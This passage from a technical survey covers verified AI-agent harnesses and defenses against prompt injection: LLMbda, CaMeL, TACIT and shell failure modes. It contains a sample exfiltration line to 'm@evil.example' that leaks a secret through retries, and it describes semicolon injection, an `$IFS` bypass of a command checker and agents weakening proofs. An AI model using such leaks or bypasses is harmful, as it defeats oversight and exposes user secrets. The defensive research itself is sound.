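When the balance is high, the program skips `rich = False`. CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when an assignment to it actually runs, so `rich` stays public and the email goes out. When the balance is low, no email goes out, so the recipient can tell the two cases apart. LLMbda programs have no variables that they can reassign. The one thing they can change is the conversation, and the interpreter refuses to add a message to a public conversation from inside a secret branch. (CaMeL has a further leak in its retry loop, which runs outside the label tracking: repeated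 attempts can reveal a whole secret one bit at a time.)

The main theorem about LLMbda is a form of noninterference. Suppose an observer may see only values up to some label m, and two starting points differ only in values the observer may not see. Then the observer can't tell from the visible results which starting point the program had, except through whether the run finishes.

```
P ~ₘ Q   →   ⟦P⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦Q⟧ₘ
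```

P and Q are programs with their conversations, and `~ₘ` means that they look the same to the observer. `⟦P⟧ₘ` gives the probability of each result as the observer sees it. `⌣` means "compatible", which requires a single list of probabilities that totals at most 1 and in which every entry is at least as large as the corresponding entries for P and Q.

For example, suppose a run ends in "done" with probability 0.6 under one password and 0.9 under another, and otherwise never finishes. These probabilities are compatible, because a list with 0.9 for "done" is at least as large as both. Suppose instead that the run ends in "a" with probability 0.6 under one password and in "b" with probability 0.6 under the other. A common list would need 0.6 for each, a total of 1.2, so the theorem rules this program out. If both runs always finish, compatible probabilities must be equal.

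The same theorem applies to hostile instructions if the observer sees only trusted values. In that case, an attacker's text can't influence any result the interpreter labels as trusted.

Like the secrecy properties discussed earlier, noninterference compares pairs of runs. Garby and colleagues prove it by defining a second set of rules for running programs. Under these rules, the interpreter skips any computation as soon as its label exceeds m and returns an empty record. Skipping can only make a program finish more often, so each probability is at least as high as under the original rules. The skipping rules never use hidden data, so P and Q get identical probabilities, which form the common list that the theorem requires.

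Strict labels would make some ordinary tasks impossible, so LLMbda has an operation called `endorse`, which relabels an untrusted value as trusted. Suppose a model with no access to tools reads an email and sorts it into one of eight categories. A program can check that the answer is one of the eight, endorse it and use it as the subject of a reply. An attacker who wrote the email can then influence which of the eight subjects is used (three bits of information), but can't insert other text. A second theorem shows that endorsing values never weakens the protection of secrets.

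### How LLMbda performed on a simulated bank

Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in LLMbda and tested it on the banking part of AgentDojo, a benchmark in which some of the data that agents read contains hidden instructions. Randori has the model write a complete plan as a program before the agent reads any outside data. If the plan fails, the model has to revise it, but an error message based on untrusted data would make the revised plan untrusted too. Randori therefore tries plans on an artificial account until one works, and only then runs that plan on the benchmark's account.

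The table gives the number of tasks completed without attacks, out of 48 (16 tasks, three attempts each).

| Setup | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Randori, labels on | 36 | 31 |
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 32 | 34 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 18 | 18 |

With only 16 different tasks, the 95% intervals extend about 20 to 27 percentage points in each direction, so the data can't distinguish Randori from CaMeL with its checks off. CaMeL did much worse with its checks on. Part of that difference may come from Randori's milder rules, since it implements only some of CaMeL's policies and lets the plan endorse untrusted data. When Garby and colleagues removed `endorse`, Randori's result with MiMo-v2.5 fell from 31 tasks to 26.

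Randori resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs, which covered 16 tasks, nine attacks and three models, with three repetitions of each combination. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The plan had to endorse those contents for the task to work. Without `endorse`, Randori blocked this attack but couldn't do the legitimate task either.

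This result is weaker evidence for the labels than it seems. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call that a plan for the user's task would not normally contain, so planning in advance usually defeats it without any label checks. CaMeL, which also plans in advance, resisted the attack in 617 of 622 completed runs with its checks off. Two of its five failures were among those 97 combinations. In both, the user had asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely, and the agent wrote a plan that could carry out an instruction for any tool, so the attacker could choose which tools to call through text in the file. The benchmark therefore shows mainly that planning in advance works well. The case for the labels rests more on the theorem, which also covers untried attacks.

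### Type-checking the code a model writes

LLMbda finds a forbidden flow while the program runs, when earlier steps may already have had effects. A compiler with a suitable type system can reject the whole program before it starts. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* describes TACIT, a tool server that accepts Scala programs from a model and runs only those that compile.

As in L3M, a capability is a value that gives access to something, such as an open file. The Scala compiler records in a function's type which capabilities the function can use. A function of type `String ->{log} Int` may use the file `log`, while a function of type `String -> Int` uses no capabilities. TACIT protects secrets by wrapping the contents of secret files in a type called `Classified`, whose `map` operation accepts only functions without capabilities.

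```scala
val secret = readClassified("secret/key.txt")

secret.map(s => s.length)                       // compiles
secret.map(s => { log.write(s); s.length })     // rejected: uses log
```

The model can therefore write code that works on a secret without receiving it. The length in the first call is also wrapped. If the program prints it, the user's terminal shows the number, but the model receives only asterisks. To summarise a secret document, the program can pass it to a separate local model that the user trusts, and the summary comes back wrapped. TACIT also compiles the model's code in a "safe mode", which forbids features such as unchecked type casts that could hide a capability from the compiler.

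This goes further than the types Eisenach and colleagues use in L3M. If an agent may read a key and push to a repository, those types don't stop it from copying the key into the repository. With `Classified`, the compiler rejects the copying.

In tests on a project with a directory of secrets, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5 each faced 131 trials, which included hidden instructions and direct requests to reveal the secrets. No secret appeared in the agent's output with the wrapper, but without it Sonnet leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax in eleven. Writing Scala instead of ordinary tool calls caused little loss in task performance. Three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 points higher on customer-service tasks, and MiniMax M2.5 scored 1.7 points lower on software repair.

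The guarantee has weaker foundations than LLMbda's. The basic type system has machine-checked proofs, but there is still no proof that safe mode delivers what it promises. The types also don't cover timing, so a program could reveal one bit of a secret by running for longer when that bit is 1. Once a program starts an external command such as `git`, the types no longer restrict what happens. Hostile text can still influence what the agent tries to do, although any code the agent writes in response must compile.

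*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a similar design in Haskell. The library's `agent` function prompts the model to write a program of whatever type the surrounding code expects. If that code expects a whole number, the generated program can't delete a file, because in Haskell any effect would change its type. The developer's own code, including the retry logic, has to pass the same type checker. A generated program can call `agent` again, but only under the same restrictions or tighter ones.

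Here too, strict rules about data keep the agent from completing some tasks. Garby and colleagues cite a test of the Haskell system on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, in which the number completed fell from 15 to 8 out of 21 once the rules were on. Many of those tasks require a flow of data that no secure policy would allow, so better tracking wouldn't let the agent complete them. Someone has to approve the exception, either by endorsing a value in the program or by answering a prompt.

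### The designs side by side

The right design depends largely on which property the developer wants to prove. Proving a limit on the number or order of actions requires a record of those actions, which commands and ledgers provide. Proving secrecy requires labels or types that follow the data through the program. All the Lean designs in the table depend on Lean and the operating system working correctly.

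| Design | Proved | Trusted | Controls the loop | Properties it can express |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Worked example | at most five tool runs, and no edit or test run without approval, in every run | the shell and the tools' code | the shell passes events to `step`, which decides what happens next | number and order of actions |
| L3M | individual checks on permissions, budgets, review and undo, but nothing about a whole session | small C files, Git and other programs, the build's linter | a sequencer in Lean | which resources a tool can reach, what L3M can undo, how much an agent may spend |
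| Agenra | quotas hold, and certified revisions preserve every workflow | the Python layer, the declarations of what tools do | the agent's Python code | how often and on what an agent may act, and where an argument came from |
| LLMbda | noninterference for every program in the language | labels on data sources, checks in the tools, the network code | an LLMbda program, which the verified interpreter runs | secrecy, and influence of untrusted data |
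| TACIT (Scala) | soundness of the basic type system, but not of safe mode | the Scala compiler and runtime, the capability library, the local model | any existing harness that can call the tool server | which effects a piece of code may use and for how long, and secrecy of wrapped data |

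## What must the shell be trusted to do, and how does it fail?

Each design in the table depends on code that its proofs don't cover. In the worked example this is the shell and the tools' own code, and `world_ok` applies to the real world only if the shell is faithful. That assumption consists of five duties:

1. Perform only the commands that the core issued.
2. Perform each command at most once.
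3. Pass every argument on unchanged.
4. Report what happened truthfully and in order.
5. Leave no other route to an effect.

The definition of `Faithful` covers some of these better than others. `noExtras` rules out extra runs, repeated runs and altered arguments, because it compares the tools that started with the tools the core requested, call by call. `truthful` covers only reports of approval. The definition doesn't cover effects that bypass the shell, because the list `w` contains only tools that the shell started, so the theorem is still true if some other program deletes `cart.py`.

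### Extra and repeated runs

Suppose a programmer wants faster feedback and makes the interpreter run the tests after every edit. In the bug fix, when the user approves the edit, the tests also run and execute code the model has just written. The user hasn't approved the test run, and the core deducts no fuel for it.

Silent retries are a more common mistake. An interpreter that repeats each failed run up to twice can turn five permitted runs into fifteen. `at_most_five` is still true because it counts commands, not runs. Retries in different layers multiply, so if a process manager below the interpreter also makes three attempts, the five runs can become 45.

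Guards that sit above the tools have the same weakness. The single-use rules of Sankar and colleagues block a second request from the agent, but the code that carries out the first request can still attempt the action again. Likewise, the Python layer in *Agenra* could run a tool twice after a single "allow".

The core never issues two `RunTool` commands with the same id (by `run_ok`), so the interpreter can catch some repeats by refusing any id it has already started. This keeps a command that enters the queue twice from running twice, but it doesn't catch a retry loop inside `runTool`, because the interpreter passes the id to `runTool` only once.

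Repeats can also come from the network. *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) examined three systems with machine-checked proofs. In one, a data store called Chapar, the servers reapplied an update whenever the network duplicated its packet, so an old value could overwrite a newer one. The proof assumed a reliable network, but the servers used UDP, which can lose, repeat or reorder packets.

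### Altered arguments and changed files

A programmer might implement the edit tool by building a command line for `sed`, a Unix program that replaces text. Suppose the user approves replacing `a and b` with `a & b`. In `sed`, `&` stands for the text that matched, so the file ends up with `a a and b b`. A file name containing a semicolon can do more damage, because the Unix shell treats whatever follows it as a new command. The interpreter can avoid both problems by writing the file itself. If it has to run other programs, it can avoid the semicolon problem by starting them directly with a list of arguments that no Unix shell parses.

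An approved command's effect can also change while its arguments stay the same. For example, a second agent in the same directory, or a process left over from an earlier call, could change the project's code between the approval and the test run. The shell still runs the tests exactly as the core asked, so it has fulfilled all five duties. The fault is in the `test` command, which has no argument that identifies the files, though a programmer can add one.

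```lean
  | test (files : Hash)    -- identifies the exact contents of the project
```

The shell fills in the hash when it turns the model's reply into an event. The hash is then part of the call that the user approved, so `run_ok` covers it too. The interpreter has to copy the project to a directory that no other program can write to, check the hash of the copy, and run the tests there. If it used the original directory instead, a file could change between the check and the run.

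Eisenach and colleagues describe a similar arrangement for building programs in L3M, split between two agents. The builder can write and compile the source but can't run the result. The runner receives the finished program, identified by its hash, but can't alter it and can write only to a fresh output directory.

### False reports and lost history

A false report of approval directly breaks the promise about approval. For example, the interpreter might treat a closed dialog window as a "yes".

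Both theorems still hold when a tool result is false, but the false result can mislead the model. Suppose the interpreter looks for "0 failed" in the test output, and the test program prints that line and then crashes. The interpreter reports success, and the model sends its closing message. Fonseca and colleagues found this kind of mistake in the build tool of IronFleet, another of the three systems. The tool read the line with the error count but not the later line reporting that the prover had died. When that happened, the tool accepted any program, including one that asserted `false`.

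Interrupts depend on the shell reporting events in the right order. If the model proposes a read just before the user presses Escape, but the shell reports the Escape first, the basic version finds nothing to stop and then starts the read.

Restarts can also introduce false information. A server in Verdi, the third system, sometimes failed to open its saved state because of a temporary error, such as too many open files. It then treated the state as missing and answered requests as though nothing had happened before the crash. If the worked example's shell handled an error opening its log the same way, it would restart from `s0` with fuel 5, and the agent could run five more tools.

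### Routes around the shell

Many programmers run a test watcher, which reruns the tests whenever a file changes. As soon as the interpreter writes an approved edit, the watcher executes the new code, even though the core never requested a test run and the shell worked correctly. Inside the harness, any plugin or library that can start a process could also run code without a request from the core, and L3M's build checks exist to prevent that.

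Information can also leak through CaMeL's retry loop, as Garby and colleagues describe. CaMeL's monitor stops a program from sending an email when the decision to send it depends on a secret value, but nothing tracks what the loop around the monitor reveals.

Suppose the secret is a bank balance between 0 and 1,023, and a hostile program contains this line:

```python
if balance >= 512: send_email("m@evil.example", "hello")
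```

If the balance is 512 or more, the monitor blocks the attempt. Otherwise the program skips the email and finishes normally. No email goes out in either case, but anyone who can see whether the monitor blocked the attempt learns which half of the range the balance is in. The next attempt tests 256 or 768, depending on the first result, and ten attempts give the exact balance.

One such bit would hardly matter. Most methods of tracking information, including LLMbda's noninterference theorem, allow a run to reveal about one bit by whether it finishes. But the loop is dangerous because it can repeat the test freely. If a core counted every attempt as an event and used up fuel for it, the number of attempts would limit the number of bits revealed. In LLMbda, programmers write the retry loop in the language itself, so the labels cover it too.

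### What if the command is a line of text for a Unix shell?

The most serious objection to the pattern is that a single command can contain almost anything. Suppose the example had a tool `bash (text : String)`, which runs a line of text in a Unix shell. The theorems would still establish that the user approved the exact text, that it ran at most once, and that no more than five tools ran, but almost nothing about what the text did. Depending on the Makefile, the line `make` could build the project, upload its source code or delete the user's home directory.

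The worked example has this problem even without `bash`. An edit can put any code into `test_cart.py`, and a test run then executes it. Two approvals, one for the edit and one for the test run, therefore let the agent do anything the user's account can do, unless something outside the core prevents it.

**Narrow commands.** Developers can replace the Unix shell with tools that each do one thing. For example, when an L3M agent asks to run a Unix command to search for text, the reviewer can point it to a search tool that needs no review. L3M's ordinary tools can start only programs from a fixed list, which contains no Unix shell or language interpreter. But agents often need more than these tools, and L3M solved about a third fewer benchmark tasks without its Unix shell. Restricting arguments also doesn't help with `make` or `pytest`, because they run the project's own code.

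*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that examines each line before the Unix shell runs it. The program first undoes simple obfuscation, then scores the line by its structure, the programs it uses, the files it touches and any known dangerous patterns it contains. It allows lines with low scores, blocks those with high scores, and sends most of the uncertain cases to a language model.

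On a balanced test set, CARE wrongly flagged 0.91% of harmless lines, and its F1 score, which combines false alarms and misses, was 85.64%. If half the lines were harmful, these figures imply that it caught about 76% of the harmful ones. In a separate test, Liu and colleagues used a sandbox to run attacks written by language models. The version of CARE without a language model reduced the rate of actual harm to 37%, so many attacks still succeeded.

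A text check has to predict how the Unix shell will read the text, and attackers look for cases where the prediction is wrong. Liu and colleagues cite a flaw in Claude Code that could let attackers bypass its check for read-only commands by using `$IFS`, a variable that the Unix shell can expand into a space. CARE also judges each line separately, so an agent could write a harmful script with one command and run it with another without either line looking dangerous.

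A sandbox restricts a process regardless of the text of the command that started it, for example by confining it to the project directory and blocking network access. *Agentao* (2026) describes a harness that combines a permission function with a sandbox. The function first returns "allow", "prompt" or "deny" for each call, and the sandbox then limits file access and Unix-shell commands at a lower level.

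A sandbox can't prevent damage to the files the agent is supposed to change, and a sandbox without network access makes it harder to install software. L3M's container plans deal with the second problem by downloading packages first, in a stage that has no access to the source code. Eisenach and colleagues proved that no stage in such a plan regains network access after private files become visible, but they had to assume that the container software follows the plan.

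**Checks at the system call.** A program reaches files and networks by making system calls to the operating system. A check at that point can examine the file actually being opened, so nobody can substitute another one after the check. L3M's C code does this when it refuses symbolic links. But the check can examine only the file and the bytes being written, so it can't distinguish a correct fix to `cart.py` from `return 5`.

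With a working sandbox, a developer could claim that at most five tools run, that the user approved every edit and test run, and that no tool reaches outside the project. The first two claims follow from the theorems if the shell is faithful, and the third depends on the operating system, but nothing establishes what a program does inside the project.

### Where faults appeared in verified software

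Fonseca and colleagues spent more than eight months reading and testing the three distributed systems and found 16 bugs. The "shim" in the table, the unverified layer between the proved code and the operating system, corresponds to the shell.

| Location | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Shim | 11 | Verdi didn't escape line breaks in arguments, so one request could run as several |
| Specification | 2 | IronFleet's specification didn't require each request to take effect only once |
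| Verification tools | 3 | IronFleet's build tool reported success after the prover had died |
| Verified protocol | 0 | none |

Five of the eleven shim bugs involved communication, three involved files on disk, and three involved resource limits. Nine of the eleven could make a server crash or hang. The researchers found no shim bugs in IronFleet, which had the fewest unverified components.

One of the resource bugs occurred in code generated from a verified function. When a Verdi server fell more than 500,000 requests behind, another server called the function recursively for each missing entry and ran out of stack memory. The proof assumed unlimited memory. The worked example could in principle fail the same way, because each `put` wraps the old table of calls in another function, and a lookup may have to pass through all of them.

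The specification bug in IronFleet would have been easy to miss because the program did remove duplicate requests. When the researchers changed seven lines to disable this, the proof still passed. Similarly, if `run_ok` omitted the clause about earlier `RunTool` commands, Lean would accept a core that ran approved calls twice.

Proofs did seem to prevent protocol mistakes. Fonseca and colleagues found 12 protocol bugs in a sample of 555 from a year of bug reports for four widely used systems without such proofs. Three of these were in LogCabin and etcd, which implement Raft, a protocol with a published formal specification. Antithesis, which sells software testing, argues in *finding bugs in raft implementations* that such code is only as reliable as its programmers' assumptions, however good the specification is. The comparison with the three research prototypes is rough because the four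 systems are much larger. The study also excluded bugs in operating systems and in the core of the provers, so it can't show how common those are.

Yang, Chen and colleagues found a similar pattern in *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (2011). They generated random programs, compared the results from different compilers, and reported more than 325 bugs. One of the compilers was CompCert, whose optimisation passes have machine-checked proofs. Six bugs that silently produced wrong code were in the unproved part of CompCert that first processes the C source. For example, CompCert compiled `-1 <= (1 && x)` to give 0 instead of 1. Two more bugs came from a description of the PowerPC processor that omitted a limit on the size of a number. There were also a handful of crashes.

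Yang and colleagues designed their test generator mainly to find bugs in compilers' optimisation passes. It found such bugs in every compiler they tested except CompCert. CompCert's developer then extended the proofs to more of the C processing. By early 2011, about six CPU-years of tests had found no wrong code from the version under development.

More recent evidence concerns Lean itself. AI agents wrote lean-zip, a compression library, and proved in Lean that decompressing a compressed file returns the original data. *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* (kirancodes.me) describes how a programmer had a Claude agent attack the library in April 2026 without telling it about the proofs. Sixteen fuzzers, programs that try huge numbers of altered inputs, made 105.8 million attempts in about 19 hours. They found no memory errors in lean-zip's own code, but they found two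 other faults.

One bug was in lean-zip's ZIP archive reader, which no theorems covered. When a 156-byte file listed the size of its contents as several exabytes, lean-zip tried to reserve that much memory and crashed.

The other was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that every compiled Lean program uses. To store n bytes, the runtime reserved n + 24 bytes. If n was 2^64 − 1, the largest 64-bit number, the sum wrapped around to 23. The runtime then read the file into a 23-byte space and could overwrite the memory after it. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.29.1* (2026) records the fix, which makes the runtime report an out-of-memory error instead. A harness written in Lean had the same fault if it let an outside party choose how many bytes to read.

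Compiled code can also behave differently from the definition used in proofs. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a Lean function that extracts part of a string. For one byte at an enormous position, the definition used in proofs gives an empty string, but the compiled version returned the whole string. The fault affected all stable Lean versions up to 4.33.1. If a core used this function to decide whether to allow a call, a theorem could guarantee that the call is refused while the running program allowed the call.

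This fault was outside the kernel, the small part of Lean that checks proofs. In an interview with Lorica (2026), *When AI Writes the Code, Who Proves It Works?*, Lean's creator, Leo de Moura, explains that trusting a proof requires trusting only the kernel, and that people can check exported proofs with several independent programs. Running a proved core also requires trusting the compiler and the runtime, which extra proof checkers don't cover.

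### How to test a shell

Contract tests run the shell without the core. Fonseca and colleagues wrote three small programs that connected directly to Verdi's shim and checked the properties the proofs assumed, such as messages arriving intact. In the worked example, a fixed list of commands can replace `step`, with at least one test for each duty.

| Duty | Test | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| Only issued commands | issue one edit | no test run starts |
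| At most once | run a test script that adds a line to a file and then fails | the file has one new line |
| Arguments unchanged | edit a file whose name contains a space and a semicolon | only that file changes |
| Truthful reports | kill the test program halfway | the event reports a kill, not a success |
| No other route | issue no commands for a minute | no new processes and no changes to project files |

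Fault injection tests a program under conditions that rarely occur on a developer's computer. Fonseca and colleagues placed a layer between the program and the operating system that duplicated and reordered packets, interrupted disk writes and returned false errors. For an agent, a developer could kill the harness after every write to the log, then restart it and compare the state with the log. The developer could also make the log impossible to open, in which case the harness should stop with an error instead of starting again with full fuel.

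Their complete set of tests detected 13 of the 16 bugs, including every shim bug except the stack overflow. But they built the tests after finding the bugs, so this doesn't show how many unknown bugs the tests would find in another shell.

Fuzzing suits the parts of a shell that read outside data, such as model replies, file names and saved logs. The lean-zip experiment shows that an AI agent can set it up and find serious faults in less than a day. AI agents can also look for race conditions, which are errors that depend on the order of events. Lorica (2026) reports in *Maybe we've been thinking about verification backwards* that Boris Cherny, the head of Claude Code, asked Claude to apply formal verification tools to Anthropic's Claude Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents. A few prompts produced 16 proposed fixes for bugs and race conditions. This shows that such tools can be useful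 on existing harness code, though it didn't prove the toolkit correct.

Developers can also compare the commands in the log with the system calls made during the run. On Linux, a tracing program such as `strace` can list every process start, file write and network connection. For the bug fix, the trace should show the edit tool writing to `cart.py` once and the test program starting once. A second start would reveal a silent retry, and a start without a matching `RunTool` would reveal a way to start programs without that command.

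The comparison needs a list of expected extra operations, because the harness also writes its log and contacts the model provider, and the test program may start other processes and save temporary files. The comparison can miss work that another program does for the harness. For example, if the harness uses a container service to run the tests, a trace of the harness shows only a message to that service. A trace also can't reveal a false approval, because it doesn't record what the user meant.

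All these methods work better on a small shell. The buggy shims, specifications and auxiliary tools in Fonseca and colleagues' study typically came to only a few hundred lines. Each system had its own shim, and the researchers recommend well-documented shims that many projects can share and test. Programmers can keep an agent's shell small by moving retries, permission rules and recovery decisions into the core, and by writing one short case for each command. If the interpreter can't determine whether a tool succeeded, it should report that the outcome is unknown and let the core decide what to do next.

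## Who writes the core and its proofs, and how much work is it?

Until recently, specialists wrote machine-checked proofs by hand, and a proof usually took far more work than the program it covered. AI agents now write many such proofs in minutes or hours. People still have to decide what the theorems should state and make sure that an agent proves them instead of weakening them.

### Proofs written by hand

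The usual reference point is seL4, an operating-system kernel (the part of an operating system that controls the hardware and every other program). In 2009, its team finished the first full proof that the kernel's C code always follows a mathematical description of what the kernel should do. Klein, Andronick and colleagues report in *seL4* that the design and code took about 30 person-months and the proof about 20 person-years. Nine of those person-years went into tools and libraries, and the team expected a similar proof for a new kernel to take six.

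The team also started from something like a pure core, a prototype written in Haskell, where effects are explicit. They then rewrote it by hand in fast C. Proving that the prototype's design follows the mathematical description took eight person-years, 80% of which went into invariants. Proving that the C code follows the design took three more. Trustworthy Systems' *Proof Statistics* reports 160 bugs in the C code, 144 of which were found during the proof work.

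The worked example needs much less effort than seL4 because its theorems cover only the number and order of tool runs, while seL4's cover everything the kernel does. *From Formal Methods to Fuzzing and Back* (2026) gives figures that work out to about 19 lines of proof per line of C for seL4 and just over five per line of compiler code for CompCert. It also cites a study suggesting that proof size grows with the square of statement size. Doubling the length of a theorem statement may therefore quadruple the length of its proof, which is a good reason to keep the theorem statements about a core short.

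### An interpreter written and proved in 30 minutes

Fang and Xiong (2026), in *Trustworthy Software Project Generation*, had an AI system write an interpreter for RISC-V, an open standard for processor instructions. The interpreter is a program that imitates a processor, and it had to handle 47 instructions. Functions in Rocq are pure, so the system first had to separate the decisions from the effects:

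1. One agent turned the text of the RISC-V manual into a plan. The plan listed the data types, the pure functions, the properties to prove, and the operations to leave to C++, such as input and output.
2. A second agent wrote the functions in Rocq.
3. A third agent stated the properties as theorems and proved them. When Rocq rejected a proof, the agent received the error and the goal that remained open.
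4. A translation tool called Crane turned the accepted functions into C++, and the AI system added the code for the effects.

The main function, also called `step`, takes the processor's state and an instruction and returns the next state. One instruction, JALR, computes a target address by adding an offset to a register's value and clearing the lowest bit of the sum. It then saves the address of the following instruction and jumps to the target. The agents proved that JALR saves the right address, jumps to the right place, always jumps to an even address, and leaves the rest of the state unchanged.

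The system finished within the 30-minute limit, using Claude Opus 4.7 and about 21 million tokens. No person intervened after the start.

| Part | Lines | Evidence that it is correct |
|---|---|---|
| Types and functions in Rocq | 937 | machine-checked theorems |
| Theorems and proofs in Rocq | 922 | Rocq checked the proofs, but nobody compared the theorems with the manual |
| C++ translated from the functions | 2,848 | the theorems, if Crane translates correctly, and tests |
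| C++ for the effects | 88 | tests only |

The finished program passed all 265 tests, and 12 hours of fuzzing with 98.2 million inputs caused no crashes or hangs. This is limited evidence of correctness because the same model wrote the functions, theorems and tests, and it could have misread the manual in the same way in all three. The fuzzing checked only for crashes and hangs, not for wrong results. The translation also needs care because it turns Rocq integers, which have no size limit, into 64-bit C++ integers.

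A proof can add little when the theorem is stated in terms of the code it checks. The JALR code computes the new address with a helper function, `jalr_target`, and the theorem about the address states that the result equals `jalr_target` of the sum. If the helper also added 4 by mistake, this theorem would still hold, and so would the one about even addresses. To catch that mistake, someone has to read the helper or prove a separate theorem about it.

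Fang and Xiong repeated the task with Dafny, a language that passes its proofs to an automatic solver. After 30 minutes the agent had written 2,070 lines but hadn't finished the verification. Solver timeouts gave the agent no useful information about what was missing, so it kept trying new formulations that also timed out. Rocq shows which goals remain open, which plausibly explains why the agent succeeded with it, but one run with each language can't establish that Rocq is generally better for AI agents.

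### How much verified code can AI write?

AI systems can now solve nearly all the problems in benchmarks made of single functions. In *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* (Yao, 2026), GPT-5.4 produced verified code for 95.0% of 423 Lean specifications, using up to 50 model calls for each.

*Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification* (Ganguly, Raghunathan and colleagues, 2026) reports the newest results. Its system, EasyProver, runs Anthropic's Fable 5 as a group of agents that delegate parts of a proof to one another. Given a statement, EasyProver must prove either it or its negation. It did one or the other for all 189 tasks in the benchmark VERINA and for 597 of 600 in NTP4VC, a set of proof obligations from industrial code. When VERINA came out in 2025, the best model proved 4.9% of the tasks in one attempt.

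Ganguly and colleagues then made a harder test from Rust code translated into Lean, where proofs must deal with integer overflow, loops and array bounds. EasyProver proved 52.7% of the 2,000 statements in 30 minutes each. It proved 84.1% of those about special cases, but only 31.0% of those that gave an explicit contract for a function. Some of the unproved statements may be false, so even a perfect prover might not reach 100%.

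Whole projects are also harder than single functions. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) gave agents 43 Lean projects with fixed specifications and asked for both the code and the proofs. The best agent, Codex with GPT-5.5, satisfied 87.3% of the specifications in 90-minute runs but completed only 27 projects. The specifications it missed tended to depend on a few shared invariants that it never found. In the worked example, an agent with the same weakness might prove that ids are always new but fail to find the combination of four statements in `Inv`.

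The agents in Ye and colleagues' tests also settled on an implementation early and rarely changed it when a proof got stuck. In five runs, an agent replaced a complicated algorithm with a simpler, slower one that satisfied the same specifications, then proved all of them. An AI agent's core can often use a simpler, slower algorithm too, because it does little computing between slow model calls.

### A complete web application

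*A complete production webapp in Lean* (Butcher, 2026) describes a to-do list application with sign-in, a database, an AI assistant, and tools that a user's own agent can call. One theorem, `nothing_mutates_without_write`, shows that an agent whose access token lacks write permission can't reach any tool that changes something. Another shows that a conversation read back from the database is the one the application stored, which matters because the application sends the whole conversation to the model on every turn. A third shows that refusing a sign-in never reveals who owns an email address.

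Butcher also found that AI coding agents produced higher-quality work in Lean, with fewer tokens and far fewer rounds of debugging. This is one programmer's experience, without measurements, but it shows that a single developer can now put such theorems into an ordinary application.

### Keeping proofs up to date

A small change to a program can require a large change to its proof. When the seL4 team added a system call that combined existing ones, writing the code took a day and proving it correct took less than a week. Another change affected under 5% of the code but broke important invariants, and Klein and colleagues report that proving the kernel correct again took about a person-year.

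Suppose the developers of the worked example add an "always allow edits" option. `run_ok` is then false, because an edit can run without its own approval. They need a new theorem that states exactly when this may happen. An AI agent told only to make the proof compile could instead add the premise that the option is off. Lean would accept the proof, but the theorem would no longer cover anyone who uses the option.

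Something similar happened in a real project, although the faulty condition came from an older, human-written proof. *AI-Assisted Completion of CertiGC Proofs* (Wang, 2026) describes a verified garbage collector, a component that frees memory a program no longer needs. The original proof assumed that older objects never point to newer ones. A new version let programs modify existing objects, so the assumption became false. Codex proposed replacing it with the condition that the collector keeps a record of every pointer from an older object to a newer one, and Wang judged this condition correct.

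Rocq accepted the main theorem about a week after the AI-assisted work began. Two days later, an audit found the old assumption still in the specification that connects the C code to the theorem. Until Wang removed it, the result about the C code excluded exactly the programs the new version was meant to support. The whole repair took 59.3 hours of agent activity and 415 human prompts.

Proofs can also fail when the program hasn't changed, because a new version of the prover searches differently. *Developing Formally Proven Code with AI* (Ochem, 2026) describes seven-year-old proofs in SPARK, a language for high-reliability software, that failed with the latest prover. An AI agent repaired them in about an hour, though Ochem had expected the work to take several days. Ochem's company, AdaCore, sells SPARK tools, but the changes are public. This kind of repair suits AI well, because the prover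 can check every attempt and the theorem doesn't need to change.

### Theorems that prove too little

A proof checker can't determine whether a theorem expresses what its author wanted. In a simple example from F*'s *Getting Started*, an AI agent wrote a function that reverses a list and proved that reversing a list twice gives the original list, all for about $0.33. A function that returned every list unchanged would satisfy the same theorem.

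The promise about approval can fail in the same way. Suppose an agent writes this definition and theorem for the worked example:

```lean
def approved (tr : List Entry) (id : Nat) (t : Tool) : Prop := True

theorem run_approved (h : Reach tr s) (hc : .RunTool id t ∈ (step s e).2) :
    approved tr id t := trivial
```

`approved` is true of every call, so the proof is one word long and would work for any `step`, even though the theorem appears to guarantee that every tool run has approval. This flaw is easy to spot, but other definitions look reasonable and still allow a bad core.

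| What "approved" means in the theorem | A core that would satisfy it |
|---|---|
| Always true | runs every proposal at once |
| The user has approved some call | runs everything after the first "yes" |
| The user has approved this id | replaces the call after showing it to the user |
| The user has approved this id, and the core asked about this exact call under it | runs the approved call twice |

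`run_ok` rules out all four, but it depends on a definition too: `needsApproval`, which exempts reads and covers every other tool. If a programmer had instead listed edits and test runs as needing approval and exempted everything else, the two versions would behave the same today. But if someone later added a tool that deletes files, the second version would let it run without approval, and `run_ok` would still compile.

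Empty specifications are common in some AI-written code. In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) reproduced another group's system, which writes Dafny programs and translates them into Python. On a set of short programming tasks, Dafny accepted 99.1% of the programs. Only 5.3% of the accepted programs had a postcondition, which is a statement about what the result must be, and only 1.9% had one that used a definition from a separate specification. A useful postcondition may not need such a definition, and a useless one may include it, so the 1.9% doesn't measure how many specifications were good. But for the 94.7% without a postcondition, Dafny checked properties such as termination and proved no general statement about the answers.

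Vempaty and colleagues' system requires every component to use a named specification, but 11.5% of its fully verified programs on one Rust benchmark and 14.8% on another still failed hidden tests. Possible causes include incomplete specifications and errors in translation or in the tests.

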